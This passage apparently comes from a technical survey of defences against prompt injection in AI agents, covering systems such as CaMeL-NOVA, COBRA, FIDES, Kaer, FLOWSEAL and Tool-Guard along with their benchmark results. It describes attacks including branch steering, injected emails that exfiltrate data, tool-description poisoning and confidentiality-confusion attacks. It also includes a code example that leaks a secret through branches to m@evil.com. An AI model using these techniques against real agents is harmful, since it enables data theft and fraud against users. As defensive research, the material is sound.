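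Costa and colleagues classify only 5% of AgentDojo's office tasks and 10% of its travel tasks as data-dependent, compared with about 43% of the banking and Slack tasks. *DRIFT* (2025) highlights six AgentDojo tasks whose instructions appear only in external data, such as an email listing the week's to-dos. CaMeL completed none of them.

### Agents that operate a screen

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, January 2026) adapts CaMeL to agents that work by looking at a screen and clicking. Such an agent seems to need new information at every step, because the position of a button depends on the window and a pop-up may cover it. The adaptation relies on the situations an agent may meet at a given step being fairly predictable, even though a screen can look different in countless ways.

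The planner in the CaMeL-NOVA system writes a complete program with branches before anything appears on screen. At each step, the program calls a quarantined vision model to describe the screen, then a quarantined language model to check whether the description matches an expected condition, such as "a cookie banner is visible". The interpreter uses the true or false answer to pick a branch, which may contain a click at coordinates the vision model has supplied.

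These programs average 213 lines, 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines, 5 calls and 4 branches for CaMeL's AgentDojo programs. Roughly half of each program consists of fallbacks that a given run never uses.

Foerster and colleagues tested the system on OSWorld, a benchmark of desktop tasks such as editing a spreadsheet. They report that a large model, Claude Sonnet 4.5, retained up to 57% of its performance. Without isolation, Claude completed 109 of the tasks that software can grade. With CaMeL-NOVA, it completed 62 of those 109 (57%) within five attempts, but only 31 (28%) on the first. A user would have to recognise which attempt had worked, and a failed attempt may leave changes behind. The researchers also limited Claude to 15 steps per task, which they say explains most of the gap between its score of 37.7% without isolation and the published 58.1%.

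The researchers also report a 19% improvement for UI-TARS, a small open model. On the 339 tasks that software can grade, the undefended model completed 60. The isolated system completed 51 on its first attempt and 77 within three, so the improvement depends on the extra attempts. It also depends on having a more capable model do the planning. When the researchers swapped the vision model but kept the planner, results hardly changed. They take this as a sign that better planners will make the design more useful without weakening its security.

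Writing the whole program in advance also saves computation. CaMeL-NOVA used 1.9 times as many tokens as an undefended agent. A version based on Costa and colleagues' system, FIDES, which calls the planner again before each step, completed a similar share of tasks but used almost 30 times as many.

### Branch steering

The branches allow a new attack called branch steering, in which false observations lead the agent down a harmful branch that is already in the plan. For example, many plans include a step to close cookie banners. Foerster and colleagues made an advertisement that looked like one, and the agent clicked it and landed on the attacker's website. Control-flow integrity held because every action belonged to the plan.

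The researchers tried two defences. One compared the vision model's answer with the page's underlying code. It caught the fake banner in one common type of advertisement but missed it in another, where the attacker could write code that also described a cookie banner. The other used a second vision model to check the answer, but it had difficulty telling fake banners from real ones without blocking ordinary work. The researchers also altered the pixels of an advertisement so that the first model gave a plausible but false answer, and the second model confirmed it. Both defences depend on models recognising a deception, so they support only a robustness claim.

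The missing property is data-flow integrity, which Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues define in *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) as the requirement that outcomes, including the arguments of important actions, stay within what the user authorised even when they depend on untrusted data. Their system COBRA, published in October 2026, tries to enforce this by giving each branch its own permissions.

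COBRA's planner first writes a branching program, using the request and descriptions of websites and tools that the user has approved. If the request lacks an important value, such as a delivery address, the planner asks the user for it. A second call to a trusted model then lists, for each branch, the sites, operations and argument values that the branch may use. All this happens before the agent reads anything untrusted. While the program runs, proxies check each outgoing web request and tool call against the rules for the current branch. If the agent is inside branches *b*₁ to *b*ₙ, each nested in the one before, and *A*(*b*) is the set of requests that branch *b* allows, the proxies pass only requests in

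*A*(*b*₁) ∩ *A*(*b*₂) ∩ … ∩ *A*(*b*ₙ).

The agent can still click a fake cookie banner, but COBRA's proxy blocks the resulting request to an unapproved site. COBRA adapts this proxy from ceLLMate and checks requests rather than clicks for the same reason ceLLMate does.

Zingrillo and colleagues built a benchmark of 199 branch steering attacks. On the 74 cases that all the systems could run, the attack succeeded in 90.5% against an ordinary agent and 87.8% against CaMeL-NOVA, so control-flow integrity alone made almost no difference to these attacks. COBRA blocked all 199, but 174 succeeded when the researchers switched off the protection each case was designed to test. COBRA retained 97% of CaMeL-NOVA's utility on the benchmark's harmless tasks.

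The drawback of planning ahead is clearer on an independent set of 361 desktop tasks. The table shows the share of tasks completed within five attempts.

| Model operating the screen | Ordinary agent | COBRA |
|---|---|---|
| UI-TARS, with GPT-5 as COBRA's planner | 23.5% | 36.8% |
| Kimi K2.5, also as planner | 42.1% | 25.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 5, also as planner | 51.0% | 38.8% |

UI-TARS gained because COBRA added a much stronger model to do the planning. When the same model did both jobs, COBRA completed a quarter to two fifths fewer tasks than the ordinary agent.

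COBRA's guarantee depends on the rules it generates being correct. The researchers wrote the correct rules for 30 cases by hand, and COBRA's rules gave the right decisions in 28. Of the other two sets of rules, one blocked a legitimate operation and the other allowed an operation the user had not authorised. COBRA also needs a detailed description of each website. In tests on another benchmark, it blocked all 14 attacks that misused an approved site when it had these descriptions. Without them, it could restrict only which sites the agent contacted, and all 14 attacks succeeded.

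Some harms never appear in a request. For example, if a checkout request contains only product numbers, COBRA has to read the price from the screen, where an advertisement could show a fake price. COBRA also cannot judge the wording of a comment, and it does not check programs that write directly to files or send email without using the web.

### When the plan stops working

Xiang and colleagues object that many tasks change while the agent is working on them. For example, a planner that cannot see results keeps calling an address that a service has retired. A branch in the plan could cover that error, but branches help much less in their second example, where a programmer asks an agent to run a project's tests and fix whatever fails. One failure may come from a loop that runs once too often, another from two processes interfering with each other. Each repair changes what fails next, so nobody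 can write out all the possible repairs beforehand. Every branch that depends on the environment also gives an attacker another decision to influence.

Most benchmarks don't reveal this problem because their tasks are short and predictable. *AgentDyn* (2026) was designed to test for it, with tasks that require the agent to adapt its plan to what it finds. *AutoDojo* (2026) reports that CaMeL completed none of these tasks with any model tested. No attack on CaMeL succeeded either, but that doesn't demonstrate useful security when the agent completes no tasks. *AutoDojo* omits CaMeL from its own AgentDyn tests because CaMeL would need extensive new policies for each group of tasks, so missing policies may account for some of the failures.

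The desktop experiments suggest that planning ahead can work for more tasks than its critics expect. Zingrillo and colleagues also had the planner write five plans and merge them into one program with more fallbacks. Of 55 tasks that COBRA had completed only on a second or later attempt, the merged program completed 27 on the first. Writing fallbacks in advance works for pop-ups and moved buttons, which recur across tasks, but is unlikely to work for an unfamiliar bug.

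### Replanning without reading the attacker's text

An attacker can exploit a planner's ability to revise its plan, so Girrens and Wang do not allow revisions. SPA calls the planner once per request, and if a check rejects the plan, the planner receives no explanation and cannot try again. Otherwise, they argue, it could keep revising an unsafe plan until the checker accepted it.

DRIFT allows more risk. It plans from the user's request, then uses one model to decide whether to change the plan and another to remove suspicious text from tool results. It completed most of the open-ended AgentDojo tasks that an undefended agent could complete, but Xiang and colleagues point out that an adaptive attacker may still mislead these models.

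Models normally recognise an instruction and decide to follow it in a single step. Xiang and colleagues suggest separating the two. The model would first repeat every instruction it is going to follow. Software would then search the trusted and untrusted text to find where each one came from, and either block those from untrusted sources or ask the user about them. To ask the user less often, the agent could predict before opening a page whether the page should contain instructions. It would expect them in an installation guide, for example, but not in a news article. The proposal depends on the model accurately reporting which instructions it will follow, and Xiang and colleagues have not tested it.

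A more restrictive method passes the planner a standard error code instead of text. *Kaer* (Mallick, Rose and colleagues, 2026) applies this method to systems where a planner divides a job among several agents, any of which may be malicious. In the paper's example, a coding agent reports that it has failed and tells the planner to run a script that would send the user's API keys to an attacker. Kaer discards such messages and lets the agent report a failure only by choosing from a fixed list of conditions, such as "information not found" or "capability not granted".

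Kaer has 13 such conditions, and several can apply to one failure. The planner can therefore receive at most 2¹³ = 8,192 different reports, all of which the developers can anticipate. It responds with a combination of seven operations:

- run a step again;
- change its instructions;
- change its permissions;
- give it to another agent;
- add a step;
- remove a step;
- change which earlier results a step receives.

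Ordinary software then checks the new plan. If *C*(*a*) is the set of capabilities that agent *a* offers and *C*(*t*) the set that the user allowed for the task, every step that *a* performs may use only capabilities in

*C*(*a*) ∩ *C*(*t*).

Anything outside *C*(*t*) requires the user's approval. The software also checks that each result goes only to agents that may receive it.

In the case of the retired address, Kaer's planner would be told only that part of its instruction was wrong. It could add a step to look up the new address and pass the result on without reading it. That result might still be harmful if an attacker had altered the documentation, so the agent would also need a limit on which sites it can contact.

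Mallick and colleagues tested Kaer on 14 tasks that force a change of plan, combined with 14 attacks on the replanning. With GPT-5.6 Sol, Kaer blocked 92.3% of attacks. ControlValve, an earlier defence that fixes the permitted order of agents in advance, blocked 69.8%, and a system without defences blocked 35.0%. Without an attack, Kaer completed 64.3% of tasks and ControlValve 54.3%. In most of the attacks that Kaer failed to block, the malicious agent reported a step as successful but returned false results, which Kaer does not check by default. In a separate test, having a language model review these results raised the share of attacks blocked from 86.6% to 96.8%, though an attacker can try to mislead that model too.

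Kaer protects the plan but not the work inside each step. An agent that fixes failing tests still has to read the logs and code, and an injection in them can make it misuse whatever capabilities the step grants. A developer can limit the damage by running that agent in a sandbox with no credentials or network access, and by reviewing its changes before merging them.

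## Tracking where data came from and where it may go

Hiding every tool result from the planner prevents attackers from influencing the plan, but it also hides data that no attacker could have altered, and it does not stop the agent from sending a confidential document to someone who should not read it. Information-flow control addresses both problems by labeling each piece of data to record whether it is trustworthy and who may read it. Software carries the labels along as the agent works and checks them before each tool call. In 2025, Costa and colleagues at Microsoft built FIDES, a planner that works this way.

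### Labels and how they combine

The simplest integrity labels are "trusted" and "untrusted", and the simplest confidentiality labels are "public" and "secret". Labels have an order. The statement ℓ₁ ⊑ ℓ₂ means that ℓ₂ is at least as restrictive as ℓ₁, so data may move from a place labelled ℓ₁ to a place labelled ℓ₂. For the simple labels,

trusted ⊑ untrusted and public ⊑ secret.

Public data may go into a secret file, for example, but secret data may not go into a public one.

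When software combines two pieces of data, the result takes the join of their labels, written ℓ₁ ⊔ ℓ₂. This is the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both. A summary of a trusted email and an untrusted one is therefore untrusted. Security researchers call a set of labels with this kind of order and join a lattice.

Most organisations need finer distinctions than public and secret, so a confidentiality label can instead list everyone who may read the data. Suppose A, B and C may read one document, and B, C and D may read another. A report based on both could reveal the contents of either, so only people who may read both documents may read the report:

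{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}.

With these labels, "more restrictive" means "fewer readers", and a join never adds readers to the list. Integrity labels can likewise list everyone who could have written the data. Their join is the union of the lists, because anyone who could alter either document could have affected the report.

A FIDES label has an integrity part and a confidentiality part, and software joins each part separately.

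### The planning loop with labels

FIDES adds labels to the ordinary agent loop. In its simplest form, the loop works as follows:

1. The harness labels the developer's instructions and the user's request as trusted and public.
2. The planner adds each new message to the history and joins the message's label to the label of the history.
3. The planner sends the history to the model. The model's output takes the join of the labels on everything the model has read, including the tool descriptions.
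4. If the output is a tool call, the call and each of its arguments take the output's label.
5. Software compares these labels with the policy for that tool, and runs the tool only if the policy allows it.
6. The result takes the join of the labels on the call, its arguments and any stored data the tool may have read. Any data the tool may have changed takes the same label.
7. The result becomes the next message, and the loop returns to the second step.

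This method is called taint tracking. The model may have ignored most of its input, but software cannot tell which parts affected the output, so the method assumes that all of them did. The label on the history can therefore only become more restrictive during a task.

Costa and colleagues wrote wrapper functions that attach the labels when a tool reads data. For an email, the wrapper lists the sender and recipients as the authorised readers, although someone may have shared the email more widely. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* counts the labels and the software that propagates them as part of the trusted computing base, so a document wrongly labelled "trusted" is a security flaw.

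### The email example under two policies

FIDES relies on two basic policies. Under the trusted-action policy, a call with real consequences, such as a bank transfer, may run only if the call and its arguments are trusted. Under the permitted-flow policy, a tool may send data only to people who may read it. If *S* is the set of authorised readers and *R* the set of recipients, the policy requires

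*R* ⊆ *S*.

Suppose the user, the manager and a colleague may read the emails about Project X. The attacker sent an email only to the user, so the label on that email lists the attacker and the user. The top email in the mailbox is about salaries, and only the user and the personnel department may read it.

Once the agent has read the project emails and the attacker's email, the history is untrusted. Its authorised readers are

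{user, manager, colleague} ∩ {user, attacker} = {user}.

If the model follows the injection, it fetches the salary email and requests a call to `send_mail` with the attacker's address. The trusted-action policy blocks this call because the model chose it after reading untrusted text. The permitted-flow policy also blocks it, because the attacker is not authorised to read the history.

However, the same policies block the summary, because the model also chose that call after reading untrusted text and the manager is no longer an authorised reader. The attacker's email has shortened the list of authorised readers for everything the model writes from then on, even if the summary does not use that email. The simple loop is secure here, but it cannot do what the user asked.

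Each policy is also useful alone. With only the permitted-flow policy, an injection can still make the agent send a misleading message, but only to people who may read the information in it. With only the trusted-action policy, a user can ask the agent to send a confidential contract to an outside lawyer who is not on the list of readers. Because the request came from the user, the software treats the release as intended. Researchers call this robust declassification, since an attacker cannot trigger it. In their tests, Costa and colleagues let the agent send any email that met either policy.

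### Hiding only what would change the label

FIDES avoids the problem with the summary by using the dual-model pattern, in which the planner handles untrusted results as named variables. Unlike the strict version of that pattern, it hides a result only when showing it would make the history's label more restrictive. The software checks each field of a result separately. If a field's label satisfies

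ℓ(field) ⊑ ℓ(history),

the planner sees the contents. Otherwise the software stores the field in a variable and gives the planner only the name. The label on the history stays the same either way.

A mail server can authenticate a sender's address, for example, so an agent might treat the address as trusted and the subject and body as untrusted. The planner could then select a colleague's emails without reading any text that the colleague or an attacker wrote.

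For the Project X request, the email bodies go into variables, and the planner makes the same three calls as in the strict version. The summary is untrusted, but the planner chose to call `send_mail` based on trusted text alone. Costa and colleagues tested a version of the trusted-action policy that checks only the label on the call, so this version allows the email.

This relaxation still lets the attacker affect what the email says, as in the strict version. Requiring trusted arguments as well would prevent this, but then the agent could not send the manager any summary of untrusted emails.

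The planner can also open a variable and read it, which makes the history untrusted. In one AgentDojo task, a user asked the agent to change a password if any bank transaction looked suspicious. The amounts and dates were trusted, and the descriptions were hidden. The planner judged a payment suspicious from its size and changed the password without opening the descriptions. The policy allowed the change because the history was still trusted. A more careful agent would have read the descriptions, and the policy would then have blocked the change.

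### Answers limited to one bit

As in the earlier calendar example, the planner can ask the quarantined model a question that allows only certain answers. FIDES adds the type of the answer to its label, with types ordered by how much information they can carry:

yes or no ⊑ a choice from a fixed list ⊑ free text.

A policy can allow a consequential action to depend on an untrusted yes-or-no answer but not on untrusted text. The attacker's influence through that answer is then at most one bit.

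In another AgentDojo task, the user asks the agent to book a particular hotel in Paris if its rating is above 4. The quarantined model reads the reviews, the planner receives only a yes, and the agent makes the booking. An attacker who plants an injection in a review could turn a no into a yes, but could not change the hotel or the dates, or make the agent do anything else.

The limit applies to each answer, so a planner that asks *n* such questions gives an attacker up to *n* bits, enough to select among 2ⁿ courses of action. A single bit can also do serious harm. For example, if the agent asks whether an invoice is genuine and pays when the answer is yes, a fraudster who controls that answer can get a fake invoice paid.

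### Explicit secrecy and non-interference

The confidentiality guarantee that Costa and colleagues prove is called explicit secrecy. Let *d* be the state of all the data that the tools can read or change, with each item marked public or secret. Two states are equivalent to an outsider, written *d*₁ ≈ *d*₂, if all their public items are the same. Suppose that a run starts from *d*₁, and let *g* be the function that describes what the steps of that run do to any state. Explicit secrecy requires

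*g*(*d*₁) ≈ *g*(*d*₂) for every *d*₂ such that *d*₁ ≈ *d*₂.

Repeating the steps the agent actually performed, but on data with different secrets, must leave everything an outsider can see unchanged.

The definition holds the steps fixed, so it does not cover what an outsider can learn from the agent's choice of steps. Suppose the agent reads a secret email about layoffs and then forwards a public newsletter to an outsider only if layoffs are planned. The newsletter contains no secret, so the permitted-flow policy allows the call. Repeating the same steps with a different secret email would send the same newsletter, so explicit secrecy holds, but an outsider who knows this rule learns that layoffs are planned. The definition also does not cover secrets that can leak through the timing and length of network messages.

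Non-interference, the stronger property that monitors of a single run cannot enforce in general, does cover the choice of steps. Costa and colleagues consider it too restrictive for their loop because, after any call that might read a secret, the agent could essentially make no call that might change public data. They note that web browsers and TaintDroid, a tracking system for Android phones, also settled for a weaker property.

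Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, explain how easily leaks through branches escape a label tracker. They adapt a classic example to the language in which CaMeL's planner writes its programs. It has roughly this form:

```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold:  tmp = False
if tmp:                  rich = False
if rich:                 send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
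```

The balance is secret. If it is above the threshold, the program sets `tmp` to false, and the interpreter labels `tmp` secret. The program then skips the assignment to `rich`, which stays true. CaMeL's interpreter changes a variable's label only when the program assigns to it, so `rich` also stays public and the email goes out. If the balance is not above the threshold, the program sets `rich` to false and sends nothing. The attacker therefore learns whether the balance is above the threshold, although CaMeL would have blocked a program that tested the balance directly before sending the email.

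Garby and colleagues found a second leak outside CaMeL's interpreter. When the policy blocks a program, ordinary software that does not track labels tries again. Whether the policy blocks a program can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit of it, and repeated attempts can reveal all of it.

The proposed remedy is LLMbda, a small programming language that labels every value. Proofs checked in the proof assistant Lean show that every LLMbda program, including agents that write and run their own code, satisfies a form of non-interference. The proofs cover the interpreter that calls the model, so no surrounding layer goes untracked. The theorem still allows information to leak through whether a program finishes. Programmers can keep agents useful by moving untrusted text into separate conversations and by explicitly marking each exception to the labels.

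On AgentDojo's banking tasks, an agent written in LLMbda resisted attack in all but two of 1,296 runs. It completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did with its policy checks off, and turning those checks on halved CaMeL's utility. The two failures do not necessarily contradict the theorem, which rules out only flows that the labels and the program's exceptions do not allow.

### What the AgentDojo percentages compare

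Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with a fixed attack written by someone who knows the agent's tools. With GPT-4o and no policy checks, the attack succeeded 152 times against the basic planner and 21 times against FIDES. With policy checks on, it never succeeded against either planner. The checks therefore provided the security, and the variables affected how much work the agent could still do.

That zero comes from a manual review. AgentDojo's software recorded three successful attacks against FIDES with checks on, but the researchers rejected them. Across all the planners, they did not count an attack as successful if the policy had blocked the attacker's call, if the policy permitted the action, or if the injection changed only the wording of an answer, such as by making the agent recommend a certain hotel. Zero therefore means that no attack violated the policies. The researchers also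 labelled as untrusted every field that any AgentDojo attack targets, so the test could not show what happens when a label is missing.

The table gives the share of legitimate tasks completed when there was no attack, averaged over the four AgentDojo environments.

| Planner | GPT-4o | o1 |
|---|---|---|
| Basic, no checks | 84.3% | 84.0% |
| FIDES, no checks | 60.6% | 77.6% |
| Basic, with checks | 41.9% | 44.4% |
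| FIDES, with checks | 50.0% | 60.8% |

Costa and colleagues report that under the same policy checks, FIDES completed more tasks than a basic planner, by 8 percentage points with GPT-4o and 16 with o1, an early OpenAI reasoning model. With checks off for both, FIDES completed fewer tasks than the basic planner, by 6.3 points with o1 and 23.7 with GPT-4o.

A company deciding whether to adopt FIDES would instead want to compare FIDES, with its checks on, to an undefended agent. FIDES scored about 34 points lower with GPT-4o and 23 points lower with o1. The policy caused many of the failures by design. For example, several banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, but once the planner has read the file, the policy blocks most actions on the account.

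FIDES did not always outperform the basic planner with checks. In the travel environment, FIDES completed 41% of tasks with GPT-4o, while the basic planner completed 73%. Many travel tasks need only tools that may run after the agent has read untrusted data, so the variables added complexity without benefit. GPT-4o often confused the variables' names or failed to use the quarantined model. With o1, FIDES completed 68% of the tasks.

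Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, object to comparing secure agents with undefended ones, which act without permission, because many commercial agents ask the user to approve each consequential action. They therefore count how many tasks an agent completes without needing approval. With OpenAI's o3-mini, a basic planner that asked about every consequential action completed 24.3% of AgentDojo tasks without approval. Adding labels, so that the planner asked only about calls that failed a policy check, raised this to 35.5%, and FIDES reached 50.1%.

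This is a fairer comparison for companies that would otherwise rely on approvals. It assumes that users reject every attack they are asked about, which the approval studies contradict. But if people often approve dangerous requests, a system that can decide more tool calls without asking them is more valuable.

### How restrictive labels spread

In a long task, an agent may read dozens of sources. If every output takes the join of all their labels, soon every output is untrusted and almost nobody is allowed to read it. Researchers call this label creep, label explosion or taint explosion. Keeping data in variables postpones this, but the labels spread again as soon as the planner reads a variable's contents. The quarantined model's output also always carries the labels of everything in its prompt.

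Labelling smaller pieces of data can limit the spread. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests labelling text by the message or, for a web agent, the website it came from. But the model still mixes all the pieces when it writes an answer, so finer labels help only if software can tell which pieces affected the output.

*Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models* (Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues, 2024) proposes keeping only the labels of inputs that influenced the output. The system looks for a subset of the inputs that can produce a comparable answer, and generates the answer again from that subset. For the Project X summary, it could leave out the attacker's email, and the manager would again be an authorised reader. Siddiqui and colleagues found that, in over 85% of cases in an agent setting, their method gave a less restrictive label than asking the model which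 inputs it had used. The final answer depends directly on only the chosen subset, but the choice of subset may depend on all the inputs, including the attacker's email.

Other researchers measure influence inside the model. Štorek, Holzer and colleagues (2026), in *GIF*, make tiny random changes to the numbers that represent a passage in the model and calculate how much the probabilities of the next token change. Let *U* be the change to the passage, *Y* the next token and τ the variance of the change. They prove that the information *Y* reveals about *U* satisfies

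*I*(*U*; *Y*) ≤ ½ log det(*I* + τ*M*) + *o*(τ),

where *I* on the right is the identity matrix and *M* is a matrix that records how sensitive the output is to changes in each direction. The last term becomes negligible compared with τ as the changes shrink.

In one example, a hiring agent receives a CV with an injected instruction to recommend the candidate at a salary of $200,000. The injected passage had an estimated influence of 82 bits on the recommendation, compared with 27 for the employer's hiring criteria and 16 for the rest of the context. Software could use this difference to block the recommendation.

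The proof covers only tiny changes to one particular prompt, while an attacker can replace whole sentences, so it does not bound what an attacker can achieve. A threshold or a second model is still needed to separate harmful influences from harmless ones. In tests of GIF as a detector, software examined the 50 most influential tokens, with the malicious or private ones already identified, and ranked a run with a violation above a run without one about 87% of the time. The method needs access to a model's internals, but a model with 0.6 billion parameters could stand in for a much larger one with almost no loss of accuracy.

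*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai and Wen, 2026) presents NeuroTaint, a system that tracks influence through paraphrases, the agent's decisions and information the agent stores for later sessions. NeuroTaint detected more flows than FIDES-style tracking on a benchmark of 400 scenarios. It analyses runs after they finish, so it can help investigators find a leak but does not prevent one.

### Declassification and endorsement

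Even accurate labels would block some legitimate work. A user may want to send a secret document to someone new, or have the agent follow instructions in an email. Information-flow systems handle these cases with controlled exceptions. Declassification releases specified secret data to someone outside its list of readers. Endorsement lets the agent treat specified untrusted data as trusted for a stated purpose.

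Researchers describe a declassification by what it releases, who may authorise it, where the data may go and when. *Agent libOS* (2026), a design for software that runs agents, makes each release valid once, for one agent, one destination and one exact message. If an injection changes the message after the user approves it, the approval no longer applies. The paper does not claim non-interference, and the system cannot control what the recipient does with the data.

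A system can endorse data automatically when the data is too limited to carry an instruction. FIDES can do this for yes-or-no answers, and Mallick and colleagues apply the same principle by using fixed error codes for replanning. Garby and colleagues criticise exceptions built into a system's general rules, because someone reviewing a run cannot tell an intended exception from a leak. They also note that FIDES's own evaluation did not use the exception for yes-or-no answers. In their LLMbda, each endorsement is a visible instruction in the program, and they prove that endorsing untrusted data does not weaken the guarantee for secret data.

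Kolluri and colleagues' agent, PRUDENTIA, asks the user for endorsements. Suppose a harmless email contains ten tasks for the agent, each requiring a consequential action. If the planner reads the email without an endorsement, the history becomes untrusted and the user has to approve ten calls. If the user endorses the email first, the history stays trusted and the agent can do all ten tasks without asking again.

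PRUDENTIA also gives the planner the labels and policies, so it can look for a plan that complies with them. The planner must explain why it needs to open a variable before it does so. These changes raised the share of AgentDojo tasks that o3-mini completed without any approval from 50.1% with FIDES to 59.1%. With o4-mini, they cut the approvals needed for all completed tasks from 36.8 to 19.2 per benchmark run, averaged over five runs. The overall completion rate fell slightly, from 75.7% to 73.2%.

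An endorsement saves time by covering many actions at once, but this also means a mistake does more damage. If the email contains an eleventh task in hidden text, the user endorses that task too, and the trusted-action policy no longer stops it. Approving each call separately would give the user a chance to notice the extra task. Kolluri and colleagues decided against a similar option for declassification because whether a disclosure is appropriate usually depends on the situation. They ask the user to approve each disclosure instead.

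Digital signatures could support some endorsements. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests that an agent might treat signed documentation from a known software maintainer less restrictively than an anonymous web page. But a signature proves only who wrote something, not that it is safe or correct, so an explicit policy should still determine what the agent may do with it.

### FLOWSEAL

An outsider may be able to talk an agent into revealing a secret without injecting any instructions into its data. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) studies an agent that works for Jane and knows Mark's mental-health diagnosis. Mark's former wife, Emily, wants to learn it.

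The researchers devised three attacks. In the first, Emily shares a page for a joint project and leaves a section for Jane's notes about Mark. In the second, she lists true and false statements about his health and asks the agent to delete the errors, so that whatever remains is true. In the third, she asks by email for a one-word reply, while the request for the details is on a shared page. They tested these on an agent prompted to verify the requester's identity and obtain Mark's consent. The first attack revealed 52.2% of the sensitive items, the second 75.6% and the third 43.8%, mostly because the agent did not recognise that anyone was requesting information.

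Their defence, FLOWSEAL, registers sensitive records in advance with their owners and authorised recipients. It has three confidentiality levels, for outsiders, the agent and the owner of the data:

outsider ⊑ agent ⊑ owner.

Software tracks which records the agent has read and intercepts every call that writes or shares data. It allows calls to recipients the owner has approved and blocks calls to those on a blacklist. For any other recipient, it sends only the protected records and the proposed output to a separate language model, which returns "safe" or "blocked". Emily cannot mislead this model about the purpose of the message because it does not receive her request.

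With FLOWSEAL, the three attacks revealed 0.5%, 2.3% and 2.2% of the items, and the leak rate across all the attacks tested ranged from 0% to 3.3%. The agent completed 72.4% of harmless tasks with FLOWSEAL and 75.9% with the best prompt-based defence. In a small test with real Gmail and Notion accounts, the deletion attack revealed 34.7% of the items under another defence and none under FLOWSEAL.

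Shim and colleagues prove that no content derived from a protected record can reach an unauthorised outsider unless the checker wrongly returns "safe". This exception is important because, once the agent has read a protected record, the labels alone would block everything it writes to an unknown recipient, however harmless. Whether each such message is sent therefore depends on the checker. The researchers measured how much the checker and the other components each contribute by changing one at a time. The leak rates below are for the joint-project attack.

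| Version of FLOWSEAL | Sensitive items leaked | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Complete | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| Checker always answers "blocked" | 1.3% | 0% |
| Checker always answers "safe" | 24.9% | 79.4% |
| No interception of calls | 28.4% | 81.2% |
| No privacy instructions for the agent | 8.8% | 74.4% |

The checker provides nearly all of the useful separation between harmless messages and leaks, so in practice FLOWSEAL's protection is a robustness claim. The software guarantees that the checker runs on every relevant call, but not that it is right. It most often fails by missing a paraphrased secret, and Shim and colleagues suggest that an attacker might also split a fact across several messages that each look harmless. Leaks rose from 0.5% to 8.8% when the agent's instructions were removed (last row), which weakens their argument that those instructions are not critical to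 security.

Shim and colleagues exclude prompt injection from their threat model, so we can't tell from these results how FLOWSEAL would perform against the attack on the email agent. They did not test FIDES. They describe it as leaving policy enforcement to the language model, but in Costa and colleagues' design, ordinary software checks the labels before each call. FIDES could also block the deletion attack if its policy treated a deletion on a shared page as sending data, because the model would have chosen which entries to delete after reading Mark's record.

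FLOWSEAL also blocks many disclosures that the owner would allow. When Mark was willing to consent to a legitimate request, the agent with FLOWSEAL delivered the information in 32.7% of cases, compared with 61% to 86% for the prompt-based defences, partly because it asked for his consent less often.

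## Tools, memory and other agents that cannot be trusted

Fixed plans and label rules protect an agent's decisions from untrusted data, but they assume that some inputs can be trusted. Costa and colleagues trust the tool descriptions, although strangers write many of the tools that agents use. Most tests begin with an empty history, but in practice agents keep notes between sessions and shorten long histories. They also pass work to other agents.

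### Tool descriptions

Many agents get their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common format in which a server lists its tools and runs them on request. The list gives each tool's name, a description in ordinary language and the arguments the tool accepts. The harness puts the descriptions in the first prompt, before the agent reads any data.

A malicious server can hide an instruction in a tool's description. *Think Twice Before You Act* (Shi, Wang and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a tool for checking a bank balance, whose description includes an instruction to transfer $100 to the attacker first, supposedly as a security check. The poisoned tool never has to run. Its description stays in the context at every step and makes the model misuse a different tool that the user trusts. A weather tool's description could make the email agent forward the user's mail.

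Separating the plan from the data does not prevent attacks through tool descriptions. A planner that never reads an email still reads these descriptions, so an attacker who writes one can add a call to the plan. The software then executes that call as a legitimate part of the plan.

Labelling tool descriptions as untrusted is safe but limits the agent, because its history is then untrusted from the first step. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) considers a rule that withdraws most of an agent's tools once the agent reads untrusted text. Under this rule, an agent with untrusted tool descriptions loses most of its tools as soon as the session starts.

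Policies that a model generates have the same weakness, because the model reads the tool descriptions too. Shi, Wang and colleagues wrote descriptions to mislead the policy generators in Progent and DRIFT, and tested them on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. Progent reduced the attack's success rate only from 32% to 20%, and utility fell from 73% to 43%. DRIFT did not reduce the success rate. A handwritten rule does not depend on tool descriptions, so the fixed email policy would still refuse a message to attacker@evil.com.

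Under the Model Context Protocol specification (2025), developers should treat tool descriptions as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. In *MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks*, Shaikh and Montaruli (2026) examined 11 agent frameworks and OpenAI's plain interface, and found that none deliberately checked tool descriptions. Across 18 models and 45 attacks, the attacks succeeded in 22.9% of runs. Success rates depended far more on the model than on the framework, ranging from 0.4% for Claude Fable 5 to 49.7% for Amazon Nova Pro. In 4 of the 10 runs where an attack succeeded against Claude Sonnet 5, the model identified the injection in writing but still made the tool call the attacker wanted.

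Most of these successes were counted because the agent issued the attacker's call. The planted secret reached the researchers' server in only 12% of them, partly because many calls went to dummy tools that recorded the request without sending anything. A scanner that looked for suspicious patterns rejected 20 of the 45 attacks, along with 7.2% of harmless descriptions. The researchers sent five reports to four vendors, which rejected all five.

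Trust labels achieve little unless software enforces them. In *WebMCP-Phalanx* (2026), 89% of description injections still succeeded against a browser agent that received labels without enforcement.

### Isolated planning

Removing every tool whose description mentions another tool would break legitimate work. A bank's transfer tool may properly require an identity check first, for example. Shi, Wang and colleagues instead built Tool-Guard, which keeps all the tools but limits which descriptions the planner sees together:

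1. All tools start on one list, and the planner proposes a call.
2. A language model checks whether the tool fits the user's task and the steps so far.
3. A second check by a language model asks whether the arguments come from the user's request or earlier results.
4. If either check fails, Tool-Guard discards the call and moves the tool to a second list.
5. The planner tries again, considering each list without the descriptions on the other.

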